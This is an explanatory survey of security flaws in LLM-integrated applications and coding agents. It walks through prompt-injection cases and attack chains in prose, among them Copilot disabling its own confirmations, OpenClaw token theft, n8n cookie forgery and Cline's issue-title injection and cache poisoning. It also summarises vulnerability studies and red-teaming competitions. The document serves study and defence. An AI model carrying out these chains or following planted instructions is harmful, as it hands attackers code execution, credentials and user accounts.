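File-writing tools are especially dangerous when they can edit a file that controls what the agent may do. GitHub Copilot's agent mode in the code editor VS Code normally needed the user's confirmation before running a terminal command. But it could edit files in the project folder without confirmation, including one that held the editor's settings.

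Ordinary installations of VS Code included an experimental setting that turned off all confirmations. Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot* documents an attack by the security researcher Johann Rehberger that used this setting (CVE-2025-53773). An attacker could plant an instruction, for example in a source file or a web page, telling the agent to add the setting to the project's settings file. VS Code applied the change immediately, and the agent could then run any terminal command without asking the user.

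GitHub's *Safeguarding VS Code against prompt injections* explains that the editor saved the model's edits to disk before users could review them. The buttons to keep or undo each edit looked like an approval step, but "keep" did nothing, and "undo" came too late if another part of the editor had already acted on the file.

A GitHub researcher exploited the same weakness through a different file. VS Code keeps a list of MCP servers and the command that starts each one. An instruction planted in a GitHub issue made the agent replace one of these commands. The editor then reloaded its settings and ran the new command, which opened the calculator before the researcher could review the edit. In this version, the agent only had to write to a file and did not need the terminal tool, because the editor runs the commands listed in that file.

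The design mistake was storing the agent's permissions where the agent could change them. Rehberger found other risky files that the agent could also change, including one that defines tasks for the editor to run. When developers use several agents in one project, one agent may also be able to rewrite another's permissions.

Rehberger reported the flaw on 29 June 2025, and Microsoft, which was already tracking it, released a fix in August. According to GitHub, VS Code stopped the agent from editing files outside the project folder, which blocks the attack on the user's general settings. A project's own settings file is inside that folder, so the developers were also adding a confirmation step that, unlike the earlier one, comes before any edit to a sensitive file.

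The problem extends beyond Copilot. In *Takedown*, Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025) analysed eight coding agents and got five to execute arbitrary commands without the user's approval. They combined weaknesses in different parts of each agent, such as its file tools and approval mechanism.

### Replies that a browser or template engine runs

A chat reply can contain HTML, the language of web pages, and HTML can contain scripts. Most web frameworks therefore sanitise text from outsiders, removing or disabling anything a browser might run. ChuanhuChatGPT, a web interface for chatting with models, had this protection switched off for its chat window. A script in the model's reply could therefore run in the browser of anyone who opened the conversation, a flaw known as cross-site scripting (CVE-2024-3402). The script can act on the site as the person viewing the page, but it does not control the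 server.

Where the developer puts the sanitiser matters. Ma and colleagues describe an AI agent that tried to repair this flaw by sanitising messages in the loop that normally prepares them for display. This stopped three variants of the attack, but a fourth got through because messages that already had a certain wrapper left the loop before reaching the new code. The correct repair turned sanitising back on in the display component, which every message has to pass through.

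Checking the user's prompt for scripts would not solve this either, because a script may not be in readable form until the model produces it. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian discuss an attack on DeepSeek's chat page in which the prompt contained only an encoded string. The model decoded it, and the page displayed the resulting HTML, whose script could read the user's session data.

If the renderer is on the server, the result can be full remote code execution. A template engine such as Jinja2 builds pages from templates by evaluating the expressions marked in their text. An application can safely insert the model's reply into a template as a value, but Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe an agent application that used the reply as the template itself. Jinja2 then ran any expression in the reply on the server, and an attacker could reach the operating system through the same links between Python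 objects as in the Semantic Kernel attack.

### A parser that runs what it reads

Code can run even before the application decides whether to carry out a tool call. vLLM is a server program that runs language models for other software. Its parser has to convert each parameter of a tool call from text into the right type, such as a number or a list.

For the model Qwen3-Coder, the parser used `eval()` to convert parameters of unknown type. `eval()` turns the text "[1, 2]" into a list, but it also runs any other Python expression. An attacker who got the model to put code in such a parameter could run it on the server (CVE-2025-9141). According to GitHub's *GHSA-79J6-G2M3-JGFW* (2025), the attack worked only if the server's operator had enabled tool calling and selected this parser, and the parameter had no recognised type. The attacker also needed valid login credentials, which is why Red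 Hat's *CVE-2025-9141* rates the flaw as important, not critical. Version 0.10.0 had the flaw, and version 0.10.1.1 fixed it.

An application that checks every tool call and refuses suspicious ones is still exposed to this flaw, because it checks the parser's output. By the time it refuses a call, the parser has already run the code in the parameter. Instead of `eval()`, the developer could have used `ast.literal_eval()`, a standard Python function that converts plain values such as numbers and lists without running code.

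Parsers can also cause trouble without running anything. Two parsers may read the same tool call differently, and *Oops!... I Parsed It Again* (Santos-Grueiro and Romero-Ruiz, 2026) shows that a security check can then approve one action while the executor performs another.

### Is the model at fault?

Microsoft attributes its two flaws to the agent's architecture and the design of its tools. It says the model "isn't the issue", because the model turned language into tool calls, as designed. Developers should therefore treat every tool parameter that the model can influence as if an attacker had written it.

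These flaws can be repaired without changing the model. Both Semantic Kernel fixes work with any model because they changed only the framework. Snyk first confirmed the AWS flaw by sending the command to the server from a testing program, without a model, so the server was unsafe regardless of how a model behaved. Ma and colleagues could also test repairs without a live model, by replaying the same malicious outputs.

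But the model greatly affects how often an attack succeeds. Reiner already knew how to escape from the LoLLMs calculator, but the OpenAI model behind it would not pass on the malicious expression when asked to calculate it or to output the finished tool call. It complied on the third approach, when Reiner presented the task as help with formatting. Success also varied widely between models in the TicketOracle experiment, though that experiment tested web requests, not code execution. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian conclude that the flaw is in the application, but that the chance of exploiting it depends strongly on the model.

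The model also probably doesn't always behave as designed. In the hotel finder, the person typing was the attacker, and the model did roughly what that person asked. In the Copilot attacks, the user wanted a summary of a GitHub issue or help with a file, but the model followed a stranger's instructions instead. GitHub, which Microsoft owns, attributes this to the model confusing instructions with data, which VS Code cannot control. Michael Stepankin, whom The Stack names as the GitHub researcher behind the tests, found Claude Sonnet 4 the most resistant model, though it could still be tricked reliably. These models are from 2025, and newer ones may do better.

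"Architecture" also covers the work of several parties. A developer who built a hotel finder with Semantic Kernel's default settings never wrote `eval()` and may not have known it was there. Advice to distrust the model's parameters is hard to follow when the unsafe code is inside a framework that the developer installed to avoid writing such code. In this case, the framework's maintainers had to fix the code, and developers who used the framework had to install the fix.

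The claim fits coding agents least well. A hotel search doesn't need to run Python from a city name, so its developers can remove that ability. A coding agent has to run commands to test the software it writes, and harmful commands go through the same terminal tool as useful ones. Its developers can protect the settings file and restrict what the terminal can access, but within those limits, whether a planted instruction becomes a running command still depends partly on whether the model follows it.

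## How does a data leak lead to code execution?

"Escalation" can mean that the same injected text does more harm in one application than in another because the model has a more powerful tool. It can also mean that an attacker obtains data, such as an access token, and uses it to get further into the system. Both can involve leaks and code execution, but a leak leads to code execution only in the second case, when the stolen data gives the attacker new access.

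### The same injection with a stronger tool

NVIDIA's *Securing LLM Systems Against Prompt Injection* describes three flaws that the company's AI red team verified in LangChain in 2023. Each was in a "chain", a ready-made component that connects a model to another service.

- One chain passed the model's output to a database, which allowed SQL injection (CVE-2023-32785).
- Another requested whatever web address the model supplied, which allowed SSRF (CVE-2023-32786).
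- A third, for maths problems, passed the output to a Python interpreter, which allowed remote code execution (CVE-2023-29374, with a severity score of 9.8).

The researchers used the same OpenAI model for all three attacks. Each time, they typed an instruction where the application expected a question, and the model followed it. The wording varied a little, but the damage depended on where the application sent the model's output. LangChain blocked the route NVIDIA had used to attack the maths chain, and later removed all three components from its core library.

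Tools form a rough scale by what they can do:

| Level | What the tool can do | Example | What an attacker can gain |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read | Return stored data | A chatbot that looks up orders | Other people's data |
| Request | Send requests to other machines | LangChain's API chain | Access to services inside the network |
| Write | Change records or files | The job-site chatbot that replaced a user's email address | Altered data, or a file that another program acts on |
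| Execute | Run commands or programs | LangChain's maths chain | Control of a process and whatever it can reach |

LangChain's SQL chain could be at "read" or "write", depending on what its database account was allowed to do.

An attacker can't move up this scale by rewording the injected text. If the only tool returns opening hours, the worst result is a wrong answer about them. But the levels overlap in badly designed systems. TicketOracle's tool could only send requests, but one of those requests deleted a record. Copilot's agent in VS Code could edit a settings file without approval, and the edit gave it permission to run commands. A developer therefore has to rank a tool by everything its actions can cause.

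NVIDIA also recommends limiting each tool call to the lowest privileges held by anyone who contributed text to the prompt. If the prompt includes a stranger's review, the call should have no more access than the stranger. This would limit the damage at every level, but an assistant that reads outside email would lose most of its access as soon as it opened a message.

### What a leak can open

| What leaks | What it opens | Case |
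|---|---|---|
| An agent's access token | The agent's API | OpenClaw |
| A login cookie | The victim's account | A medical chatbot |
| A key for signing logins | Any account, through forged cookies | n8n |
| Cloud credentials | Machines and data in the cloud account | Custom GPTs |
| A publishing key | The software that users download | Cline |
| File paths | The location of files worth reading or replacing | n8n |
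| Tool descriptions | The names and parameters of the model's tools | Semantic Kernel |

File paths and tool descriptions don't give an attacker access, but they make it easier to target an attack. For example, MITRE ATLAS, a public catalogue of attacks on AI systems, reproduces the prompt that exploited Semantic Kernel's hotel finder. The prompt contained the names of both the search tool and its city parameter. An attacker who didn't know these names would have had to guess them or get the chatbot to reveal them.

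### OpenClaw: a token that could switch off the safeguards

OpenClaw is an open-source personal assistant that people run on their own computers. It can read their messages, use their accounts and run commands. Its central program, the gateway, takes instructions from a browser control page that authenticates with a token. depthfirst's *1-Click RCE To Steal Your OpenClaw Data and Keys (CVE-2026-25253)* (2026) explains how a security researcher stole this token and used it to run commands.

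The control page accepted a gateway address from the link that opened it. If the link contained an attacker's address, the page saved it, connected to it immediately and sent the token there. The victim only had to visit a web page that opened such a link.

The token alone was not enough to run commands. Most users had set OpenClaw to accept connections only from their own computer, so an attacker elsewhere could not use the token. If the gateway was reachable from the internet, the attacker could log in, read the victim's data and act on their behalf. But OpenClaw still asked the user before running a dangerous command, and some users had configured it to run commands in a container, a type of sandbox.

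The researcher got past the network restriction through the victim's browser. Browsers normally prevent a website from interacting freely with programs on the visitor's computer. For WebSockets, a type of connection that stays open in both directions, browsers leave the server to enforce this restriction. OpenClaw's gateway did not enforce it, so a script on the attacker's page could connect to the gateway from inside the victim's browser.

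The safeguards were easier to remove because the gateway's own API controlled them and the token carried administrator rights. The script turned off the confirmations, set commands to run outside the container, and then ran one on the victim's computer.

| Step | Condition | Control that would have broken it |
|---|---|---|
| The control page sends the token to the attacker | The user has logged in and visits the attacker's page | Ask the user before connecting to a new gateway |
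| A script in the browser connects to the local gateway | The gateway accepts connections from any website | Check which website started the connection |
| The script turns off the safeguards | The token permits changes to safety settings | Keep these settings out of the token's reach |
| The script runs a command | The token permits commands, and no safeguard is left | Require an approval that the API cannot turn off |

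This chain leads to remote code execution without involving a language model, so a model that refused every injected instruction would not have stopped it.

OSV's *GHSA-g8p2-7wf7-98mq* (2026) gives the flaw a severity score of 8.8 and lists version 2026.1.29 as the fix. The control page now prompts the user to confirm a new gateway. That stops this leak, but a token stolen another way would be just as dangerous unless the developers also reduced its rights. Ethiack's *One-click RCE on OpenClaw in under 2 hours* reports that the company's AI penetration tester, given only the address of an OpenClaw installation, found a one-click route from token leak to command execution in about an hour and 40 minutes.

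### n8n: from reading a file to running a command

In n8n, a program for automating workflows, an attacker without an account could read the leaked data through a chatbot. In *Ni8mare*, Attias (2026) gives the flaw (CVE-2026-21858) the maximum severity score of 10.0 and estimates that it affected 100,000 servers.

The flaw was in how n8n handled files uploaded through a form. An attacker could alter the upload request to make n8n load a file from its own server instead of the uploaded one. In the demonstration SecurityWeek describes, this file went into an organisation's knowledge base, and Attias then read it by asking the chat interface about it.

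The two most important files on the server were the user database and the file containing the secret key that n8n used to sign login cookies. Security Affairs' *Ni8mare flaw gives unauthenticated control of n8n instances* explains that an attacker with both could forge an administrator's cookie and log in. As an administrator, the attacker could then add an "Execute Command" step to a workflow and run commands on the server.

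The model played only a small part in this by repeating the contents of a file that the application had put in the knowledge base, as a knowledge-base chatbot is designed to do. Checking the file's location would have prevented the leak. Without the "Execute Command" step, the attacker would still have had the data and the administrator's account, but could not have run commands this way. Version 1.121.0 fixed the flaw.

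### Cline: code execution, then a leak, then more code execution

Cline is an AI coding tool with millions of users. In December 2025 its developers set up Claude to sort new issues (bug reports and requests) on Cline's GitHub page. Anyone with a GitHub account could trigger Claude by opening an issue. The issue's title went straight into the prompt, and Claude had access to a shell.

Security researcher Adnan Khan showed in *Clinejection* (adnanthekhan, 2026) how an attacker could use an issue title to reach Cline's published software. In every test on a copy of the project, an instruction in the title made Claude install a package from an address that an attacker could control. The package included a script that ran automatically during installation, so Claude had no opportunity to inspect it.

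At this point the attacker could run code, but only on a temporary machine that could not change Cline's source code or publish anything. The attacker could get further through a cache, where GitHub keeps files from one automated job so that later jobs can reuse them. The issue-sorting job shared its cache with the job that published Cline's nightly test versions, and that job had the publishing keys. The attacker could not overwrite the cached files, but could fill the cache until GitHub deleted them and then add altered files under the same names.

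| Step | Condition | Control that would have broken it |
|---|---|---|
| An issue title makes Claude run the attacker's code | Anyone can trigger Claude, and Claude has a shell | Give Claude only tools for reading files and handling issues |
| The code puts altered files in the cache | The two jobs share a cache | Use no cache in jobs that hold publishing keys |
| The nightly job runs the altered files, which send out the keys | The job holds long-lived keys | Use credentials that expire after each release |
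| The attacker publishes an altered package | The key still works and covers ordinary releases | Give test versions a separate package and key, and check that old keys no longer work |
| Users' computers run the package's installation script | Users install the altered version | Stay on a version known to be good |

Khan reported the problem on 1 January 2026, tried several times to reach the developers, and published the details on 9 February. Cline removed the vulnerable jobs and began replacing its keys within 30 minutes, according to its *Post-mortem* (2026). But it deleted the wrong key for npm, the registry from which people download its command-line program. On 17 February someone used the remaining key to publish an altered version of the program.

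This version was available for about eight hours. *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines (grith.ai)* (2026) reports about 4,000 downloads, which may be more than the number of computers affected. The attacker added one instruction, which installed OpenClaw, and left the program itself unchanged. Cline considers the harm low because OpenClaw is a legitimate program, but the attacker could have used the same instruction to install something harmful.

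The chain therefore begins with code execution on one temporary machine, and the stolen key then let the attacker run code on the computers of everyone who installed the update.

SafeDep's *AI Agent Cline v2.3.0 Compromised* notes that nobody has publicly confirmed exactly how the attacker got the key. The evidence that the attacker used Khan's route is circumstantial but fairly strong. Several nightly jobs failed between 31 January and 3 February and showed signs of the cache-poisoning tool that Khan had published. *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent* concludes that the attacker found Khan's test attack and reused it before Khan announced the flaw.

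Cline has since removed the issue-sorting job and says that any future automation of this kind will have read-only access. Read-only access would have stopped the attack at its first step, but keys can still leak through it. MITRE ATLAS describes how Microsoft researchers tested the GitHub component that Cline had used to run Claude. Shell commands ran in a sandbox with the secrets removed, but Claude's file-reading tool ran outside it. A planted instruction made Claude use that tool to read files containing its own process's settings, including an Anthropic API key. Anthropic blocked access to these files in May 2026.

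### Two chains that stop short of running code on a server

A custom GPT is a version of ChatGPT set up for a particular purpose, and its creator can add "actions" that send requests to outside APIs. SecurityWeek reports that Jacob Krut, a security engineer at Open Security, found that OpenAI did not properly check the addresses in these actions. Krut used an action to reach the Azure Instance Metadata Service, an internal service that gives programs on a cloud machine information about that machine and can issue them credentials.

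This was server-side request forgery, but Krut did not need prompt injection because the creator of a custom GPT chooses the address directly. Underhill (2025) writes in *ChatGPT Exploited Through SSRF Flaw in Custom GPT Actions* that the flaw could expose internal metadata and potentially Azure credentials. OpenAI fixed the flaw. Cloud credentials can lead to code execution if they let the holder start machines or run commands on them, but Krut did not demonstrate this.

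Quarkslab, a security company, took over an administrator's account during an authorised attack on a customer's live system. It later rebuilt the flaws in a mock medical chatbot to explain them. The attacker began with an ordinary account and got the model to include a script in its reply. The page ran the script, but at first only in the attacker's own conversation.

Every conversation had a predictable web address, and the server did not check who was opening it, so the attacker could send the address to an administrator. When the administrator opened it, the script ran in the administrator's browser, read the login cookie and sent it to the attacker, who could then log in as the administrator.

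| Case | Step | Condition | Control that would have broken it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Custom GPT | An action sends a request to the metadata service | The creator can enter an internal address | Block internal addresses, including after redirects |
| Custom GPT | The service returns credentials | The machine has an identity with access to cloud resources | Give that identity as few rights as possible |
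| Medical chatbot | The page runs a script in the model's reply | The page treats the reply as HTML | Convert the reply to harmless text |
| Medical chatbot | An administrator opens the attacker's conversation | The server does not check who owns it | Check ownership on the server |
| Medical chatbot | The script reads the login cookie | Scripts are able to read the cookie | Mark the cookie as unreadable by scripts |
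| Medical chatbot | The attacker logs in with the cookie | The cookie is still valid | Require a fresh login for administrator functions |

The script ran only in a browser, so the chain ended in an account takeover. That is serious on a medical platform. In a product like n8n, where administrators can run commands, it would also have led to code execution.

An attacker may not need to send a link. MITRE ATLAS records a similar test of Lenovo's support chatbot, in which the researchers asked to speak to a human. When the support agent opened the saved conversation as part of the job, the script in it sent out the agent's cookie.

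### MathGPT: code execution that exposed a key

Code execution can also come before the leak. MathGPT was a public website that used GPT-3 to turn maths questions into Python code. The site ran the code and displayed it with the answer. According to MITRE ATLAS, seeing the code led a visitor to suspect that the site ran whatever code the model wrote.

The visitor confirmed this by getting the model to write a program that printed a harmless message. Another prompt produced code that listed the server's environment variables, the settings the operating system passes to a program. These included the site's GPT-3 API key, which the visitor could have used to drain the site's budget. A further prompt produced a program that never finished, and the site stopped responding until its server restarted.

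The displayed code was a useful hint, but the visitor didn't need it to run the attack. The serious leak came once the visitor could run code, because any program on the server could read the key. AVID (2023), a database of AI vulnerabilities, records that the site's operators replaced the key and began filtering some prompts. Replacing the key made the stolen one useless, but another successful injection could expose the new one. A sandbox without the key would have prevented this leak even if an attacker could still run code.

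### Is a leak the usual first step?

Most of the documented cases of code execution did not start with a data leak. If an application already runs what the model writes, an attacker has little reason to steal a key first. One prompt was enough to run code through LangChain's maths chain, MathGPT or Semantic Kernel's hotel finder. MITRE ATLAS lists a study in which researchers found 20 remote code execution flaws in 11 frameworks and showed that prompt injection could exploit them in public applications.

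A leak matters when running code requires a login or a permission. OpenClaw and n8n both had commands meant for their owners, and the stolen data let an attacker use them as the owner. The flaw in vLLM's parser is a borderline case, because a registered user could exploit it directly, but an outsider would first have had to steal login credentials.

Sometimes a leak and code execution come from the same flaw without one causing the other. Cline's Kanban server, a program for managing coding agents, accepted connections from any website, as OpenClaw's gateway had. GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Cline package* (2026) explains that a website could use such a connection to read file paths and chat messages, and to send prompts to a running agent and make it execute commands. The leaked messages might help an attacker write a more convincing prompt, but the attack doesn't require them.

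Published cases probably make direct code execution look more common, relative to chains, than it is in real attacks. Researchers can search a framework's source code for `eval()`, but to find a chain they need to know several components and how someone has connected them. Most cases in this section are also demonstrations by researchers, but the altered Cline package reached real users, and the attacker needed a stolen key to publish it.

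## How common and how severe are these flaws in real software?

Nobody knows what share of applications with an LLM-to-API interface are exploitable. Researchers have searched source code, attacked live applications and sorted through vulnerability databases, but they mostly started with software likely to have flaws or with flaws already reported.

### Working backwards from a dangerous function

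Liu, Deng and colleagues (2024), in *Demystifying RCE Vulnerabilities in LLM-Integrated Apps*, made the first systematic count. Their program, LLMSmith, searches a framework's source code for call chains. A call chain is a series of functions, each calling the next, that leads from a public function to one that runs code. LLMSmith builds the chain backwards:

1. It starts with a dangerous function, such as `exec()` or `eval()`, and looks for files that mention its name.
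2. It maps the calls in those files to find which functions call the dangerous one.
3. It then looks for the callers of those functions, and continues until it reaches a public function that accepts outside input.

In LangChain, for example, one chain starts with a function that creates an assistant for questions about a data table, and ends with `exec()`.

This method is fast because LLMSmith skips most of the code. It found 51 call chains in 11 frameworks in under a minute. The paper's text gives about 20 seconds, but its times for the individual frameworks add up to 44 seconds. PyCG, a general tool that maps a whole codebase, found 13 chains and had produced nothing for LangChain after 24 hours.

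A call chain isn't always exploitable, so the researchers checked each one by hand. They could run code of their choice through 44 of the 51. The other seven were false positives, a rate of 13.7%. In some of these, an attacker could not control the value that reached the dangerous function. In Auto-GPT, the code ran in a container isolated from the host.

The final count was 20 vulnerabilities. Nineteen allowed remote code execution, and one let an attacker read and write files. An attacker could trigger 17 of the 20 with a prompt, while the other three needed a crafted file or a direct request to an API. The vulnerabilities received 13 CVE numbers, six with a severity score of 9.8.

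### Attacking 51 applications

The researchers also attacked 51 public web applications. They found 24 by searching GitHub for projects that called one of six vulnerable functions, so they could read the source code. They found the other 27 mainly in app directories, using keywords from the vulnerable projects' descriptions.

A chatbot that cannot run code may still make up a believable result. The researchers therefore asked each application for answers that a model could not work out without running code, such as the cryptographic hash of a random string. Twenty applications passed this test. The researchers then tested for simple system commands, access to outside networks and, finally, remote control of the server.

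Researchers exploited 17 applications, 16 through remote code execution and one through SQL injection. They gained full control of the server in 14 cases, and administrator rights as well in four of those. Of the 16 remote code execution attacks, seven needed no special technique, and the other nine had to bypass the model's restrictions or limits on the code.

The 34 failures were rarely due to good security:

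| Reason the attack failed | Applications |
|---|---|
| The application malfunctioned | 13 |
| It could not run code | 10 |
| It restricted what users could enter | 3 |
| It ran generated code in the user's browser, not on the server | 2 |
| Other or unknown | 6 |

Without the 13 that malfunctioned, the researchers exploited 17 of 38 applications, or 45%.

Liu and colleagues succeeded against 58.3% of the applications whose source code they could read, but only 11.1% of the others. They attribute the difference to the advantage of seeing the code. The way they chose the applications probably contributed too, because they knew that the first group called vulnerable functions, whereas nine of the 27 applications in the second group could not run code at all.

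Studies of prompt injection alone give higher figures. *Prompt Injection attack against LLM-integrated Applications* (2023) found 31 of 36 applications susceptible, but its main attacks, which misused the model or revealed the hidden prompt, do not require running code. *Rethinking Assessments of Prompt Injection Attacks* (Cui, Wu and colleagues, 2026) tested 37 real applications and found them more vulnerable than the set-ups researchers usually test, so laboratory results may understate how often real applications follow injected instructions.

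### How many reported flaws need a model?

Many flaws in AI software have nothing to do with what a model writes. To separate these from flaws that do, Ma and colleagues built LiLCVE, a dataset published in May 2026. They searched three vulnerability databases for 230 open-source components from the target list of huntr, a platform that pays rewards ("bug bounties") for flaws in AI software, and found 2,888 different vulnerabilities.

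Five security researchers then reviewed the records by hand and reconstructed how an attack would work. They judged 2,772 to be unrelated to LLMs. Of the remaining 116 vulnerabilities, 75 were in LLM software but could be exploited without any action by a model, such as a file-access flaw that an attacker could reach with an ordinary request. The other 41 were LLM-in-the-loop vulnerabilities. The reviewers left out unclear cases, so 41 may be too low.

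Generated code was the most common of the five routes from model output to a dangerous operation, accounting for 20 of the 41 cases. Generated queries and tool actions accounted for seven each. Of the 41 cases, 21 (51.2%) were rated critical in severity.

The proportion is much higher in popular agent applications. *Security Debt in LLM Agent Applications* (Shen, Dai and colleagues, 2025) covers the 50 agent applications with the most stars on GitHub, a rough measure of popularity. It includes bug reports from the projects' own pages as well as published vulnerabilities, because developers sometimes fix a flaw without publishing it.

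Researchers found 221 vulnerabilities, 74.1% of them rated high or critical. The most common single cause, in 52 cases, was that the application passed the model's output to a tool without proper checks. Another 95 were in the user interface and had much the same causes as flaws in ordinary web applications, so a developer who protects only against prompt injection would miss them.

The study also found that 47.5% of the vulnerabilities had no proper fix. Developers had done nothing about 62, and their attempts to fix another 43 had failed. Of those attempts, 24 failed because the filters were incomplete, and in 17 others the developers had only published a warning or moved the code to a package labelled experimental.

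LangChain's PALChain component solved reasoning problems by running Python code written by a language model. Its developers blocked certain imports and functions, then extended the blocklist after researchers found a way around it. After several rounds of this, they accepted that a blocklist could not guarantee safety and moved the component to an experimental package.

### Searching thousands of projects

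*TaintP2X* (He, Wang and colleagues, 2026) uses taint analysis, which marks data from an untrusted source and follows it through a program. The tool treats a model's output as untrusted and checks whether that output can reach any of 236 dangerous functions. A language model then helps discard false alarms, such as cases where the prompt is fixed text that no outsider can influence.

TaintP2X found 27 of 35 known vulnerabilities, and LLMSmith found 17. The comparison favours TaintP2X because the 35 included SQL injection and SSRF vulnerabilities, which LLMSmith was not built to find.

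The researchers then searched 4,772 GitHub projects that had at least 50 stars, code that called a model, and at least one dangerous function. TaintP2X reported 101 suspicious paths in 75 projects. Of these paths, 74 led to code or command execution, 15 to reading or writing files, and nine to web requests.

One of the file flaws was in gpt-engineer, a tool that lets a model edit a project's code. The tool checked that each file path began with the project folder, but did so before resolving the parts of the path that mean "go up one folder", so a path from the model could pass the check and still lead outside the project.

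The researchers reported 40 of their findings to developers, who confirmed seven and fixed five. An unanswered report may still describe a real flaw, but not all of the 101 paths are proven vulnerabilities. The paper's evaluation lists 36 false alarms among 114 results, figures that do not match the 101 paths.

### Coding agents that trust a vendor's instructions

Some companies put a file called `llms.txt` on their websites to help AI agents use their products. It often includes installation instructions. *AI Coding Agents Are Installing Unknown/Untrusted Code on Corporate Networks* (Schneier, September 2026) describes a test of what happens when these instructions are wrong.

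Researchers scanned 6,214 websites of defence contractors, large technology companies and Fortune 500 companies, and found 8,265 such files. In 120 of them, each on a different site, the instructions named a software package or web domain that nobody had registered. The researchers registered a few of these names and published packages that contacted their server when a computer ran them.

Within an hour, a computer at a Fortune 500 company had done so, followed by a few dozen more at other large companies and startups. The packages also recorded which programs had started the installation, including the coding agents Claude, OpenAI's Codex and Nous Research's Hermes.

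Reports of the test differ. Tom's Hardware's *Researchers easily trick Fortune-500 companies' AI agents into running arbitrary code* names the security firm as Pandex and gives 8,565 files, with 237 faulty references. TechRadar's *Top AI tools including Claude, Codex, and Hermes installed suspicious code* gives 8,265 files, the same number as Schneier.

This remote code execution involved no prompt injection, because the agents were following instructions the vendors had written in good faith. A model that ignored every planted instruction could still install the wrong package, so the agent or the system around it would have to check who owns a package before running it.

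The test gives no attack success rate, because nobody counted the agents that read the files without installing anything. Deliberate attacks through llms.txt files seem rare so far. Common Crawl's *A Content Analysis of llms.txt Files from the July 2026 Crawl Archive* (2026) examined 584,107 of these files and found prompt injections in only a few.

References to packages that don't exist can be dangerous even when no person sets out to exploit them. Sophos' *When AI doesn't know the target is real* describes an Anthropic test in which Claude found a document that told developers to install a nonexistent Python package. Claude published a malicious package under that name in the real public registry, and 15 real systems downloaded it in the hour or so it was available.

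### Have criminals exploited these flaws?

There are a few real cases, but the evidence is thin. The altered Cline package is one, if whoever published it got the key through prompt injection. Tom's Hardware reports that the Pandex researchers found one case in which someone had already used a missing package name to spread real malware. *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, August 2026) reported that criminals were developing tools to attack AI agents through indirect prompt injection.

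Vendors often say they know of no attacks, as Microsoft did about EchoLeak. This is weak evidence that none happened, because an injected tool call can look like normal activity in the logs.

Attacks in which criminals use AI as a tool are a separate problem. VPNCentral's *Hackers Used Claude and Codex Agents in Real-World Exploitation* describes a campaign that compromised at least 14 companies, in which the attacker set the goals and Claude did most of the operational work. Such attacks can succeed against companies that use no language models, so they aren't evidence of flaws in LLM-to-API interfaces.

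Other attacks use an AI product's settings and do not need the model to follow any instruction. According to the developer's post *I handed Claude Code the keys*, a worm that infected more than 170 software packages in May 2026 also changed the settings of the coding agent Claude Code, so the worm's code ran whenever a user started a session.

### What rate can be inferred?

The four main studies give very different percentages, partly because they measure different things:

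| Study | Result | Group examined |
|---|---|---|
| Liu and colleagues | 17 of 51 exploited (33%) | Applications likely to use vulnerable functions |
| He and colleagues | 75 of 4,772 flagged (1.6%) | Popular projects with model calls and dangerous functions |
| Ma and colleagues | 41 of 2,888 needed a model (1.4%) | Reported flaws in bug-bounty targets |
| Shen and colleagues | 52 of 221 came from unchecked model output (24%) | Reported flaws in popular agent applications |

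The last two rows are shares of reported flaws, so they cannot show how likely an application is to have one. Adding the datasets' totals would also count some flaws more than once, because the datasets overlap.

The first two rows are shares of applications or projects, but neither group represents software in general. The second share also depends on what counts as a flaw. Developers confirmed only seven, in at most 0.15% of the projects. But TaintP2X missed eight of the 35 known vulnerabilities, so it probably missed others in the larger search.

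Small samples add more uncertainty. If the 51 applications had been a random sample, the 95% confidence interval would run from about 22% to 47%. For the 27 applications without readable source code, it would run from about 4% to 28%. These intervals don't account for how the researchers chose the applications.

The known flaws are probably more severe than average, because bug bounties pay more for severe flaws and so encourage researchers to look for them. A critical rating doesn't reflect how many people use the affected feature or whether anyone has attacked it.

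CVE counts are also an uneven measure. Three of the LangChain functions in the LLMSmith study share one CVE. Under its security policy, LlamaIndex generally treats SQL flaws as ineligible for a CVE because it expects developers who use its database feature to manage the risk themselves. Shen and colleagues quote a Langflow developer who likewise considered it the administrator's job to keep users from running code. Flaws in a company's private chatbot may never appear in a public database.

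This evidence can't show how common these flaws are across all software. LLMSmith's manual check, which ran code through 44 of 51 call chains, is more useful to developers. Those chains were in frameworks from 2023 and 2024, and newer models may be harder to manipulate. Still, a developer who finds a similar path from a prompt to `exec()`, with no isolation around it, should assume that an attacker can use it.

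## What has red-teaming at scale shown about relying on the model to refuse?

The best new models follow far fewer injected instructions than the models of 2023 did. Companies and researchers test whether developers can rely on these models to refuse by red-teaming them, which means making authorised attacks to find weaknesses. Thousands of people have attacked models in public competitions, and AI models now write many of the attacks.

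### From word games to agents

The early competitions tested models without tools. In HackAPrompt, participants wrote text that was combined with a developer's instructions, trying to make the model ignore those instructions and write a particular output. More than 2,800 people submitted over 600,000 prompts, according to *Ignore This Title and HackAPrompt* (2023). In Tensor Trust, an online game from the same period, players wrote instructions to guard a virtual account and tried to break into other players' accounts. Both produced large collections of attacks, but a successful attack only made a model write certain words.

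Gray Swan, an AI security company, ran a month-long competition against agents with simulated tools in spring 2025, and another, the Indirect Prompt Injection Arena, late that year. Figures for the first competition come from *Security Challenges in AI Agent Deployment* (2025), and figures for the second come from *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026).

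| | Spring 2025 | Arena, late 2025 |
|---|---|---|
| Participants | Almost 2,000 | 464 |
| Attempts | About 1.8 million | 271,588 |
| Models | 22 | 13 |
| Scenarios | 44 | 41 |
| Successful attacks | Over 62,000 | 8,648 |
| Successes per attempt | 3.4% | 3.2% |

The spring competition's organisers also report an attack success rate of 12.7%, measured as a share of user sessions rather than attempts. By that measure, instructions planted in outside content worked 27.1% of the time, and instructions typed into the chat worked 5.7% of the time. The gap also appeared for each kind of harm that participants tried to cause both ways. For leaks of confidential data, for example, the rates were 29.8% and 7.8%. Every model failed repeatedly.

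The Arena used only planted instructions, and in most scenarios the attack also had to stay hidden from the user. In one scenario, a user asks an assistant to check for urgent emails. A fake marketing email contains instructions for the assistant to mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. If the attack works, the user receives a normal-looking summary and misses the deadline.

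Attacks succeeded least often against Claude Opus 4.5, at 0.5% of attempts, and most often against Gemini 2.5 Pro, at 8.5%. Participants still broke Opus in 13 of the 37 scenarios that counted towards the results. For every model, successful attacks rose roughly in line with attempts, with no sign that participants were running out of attacks.

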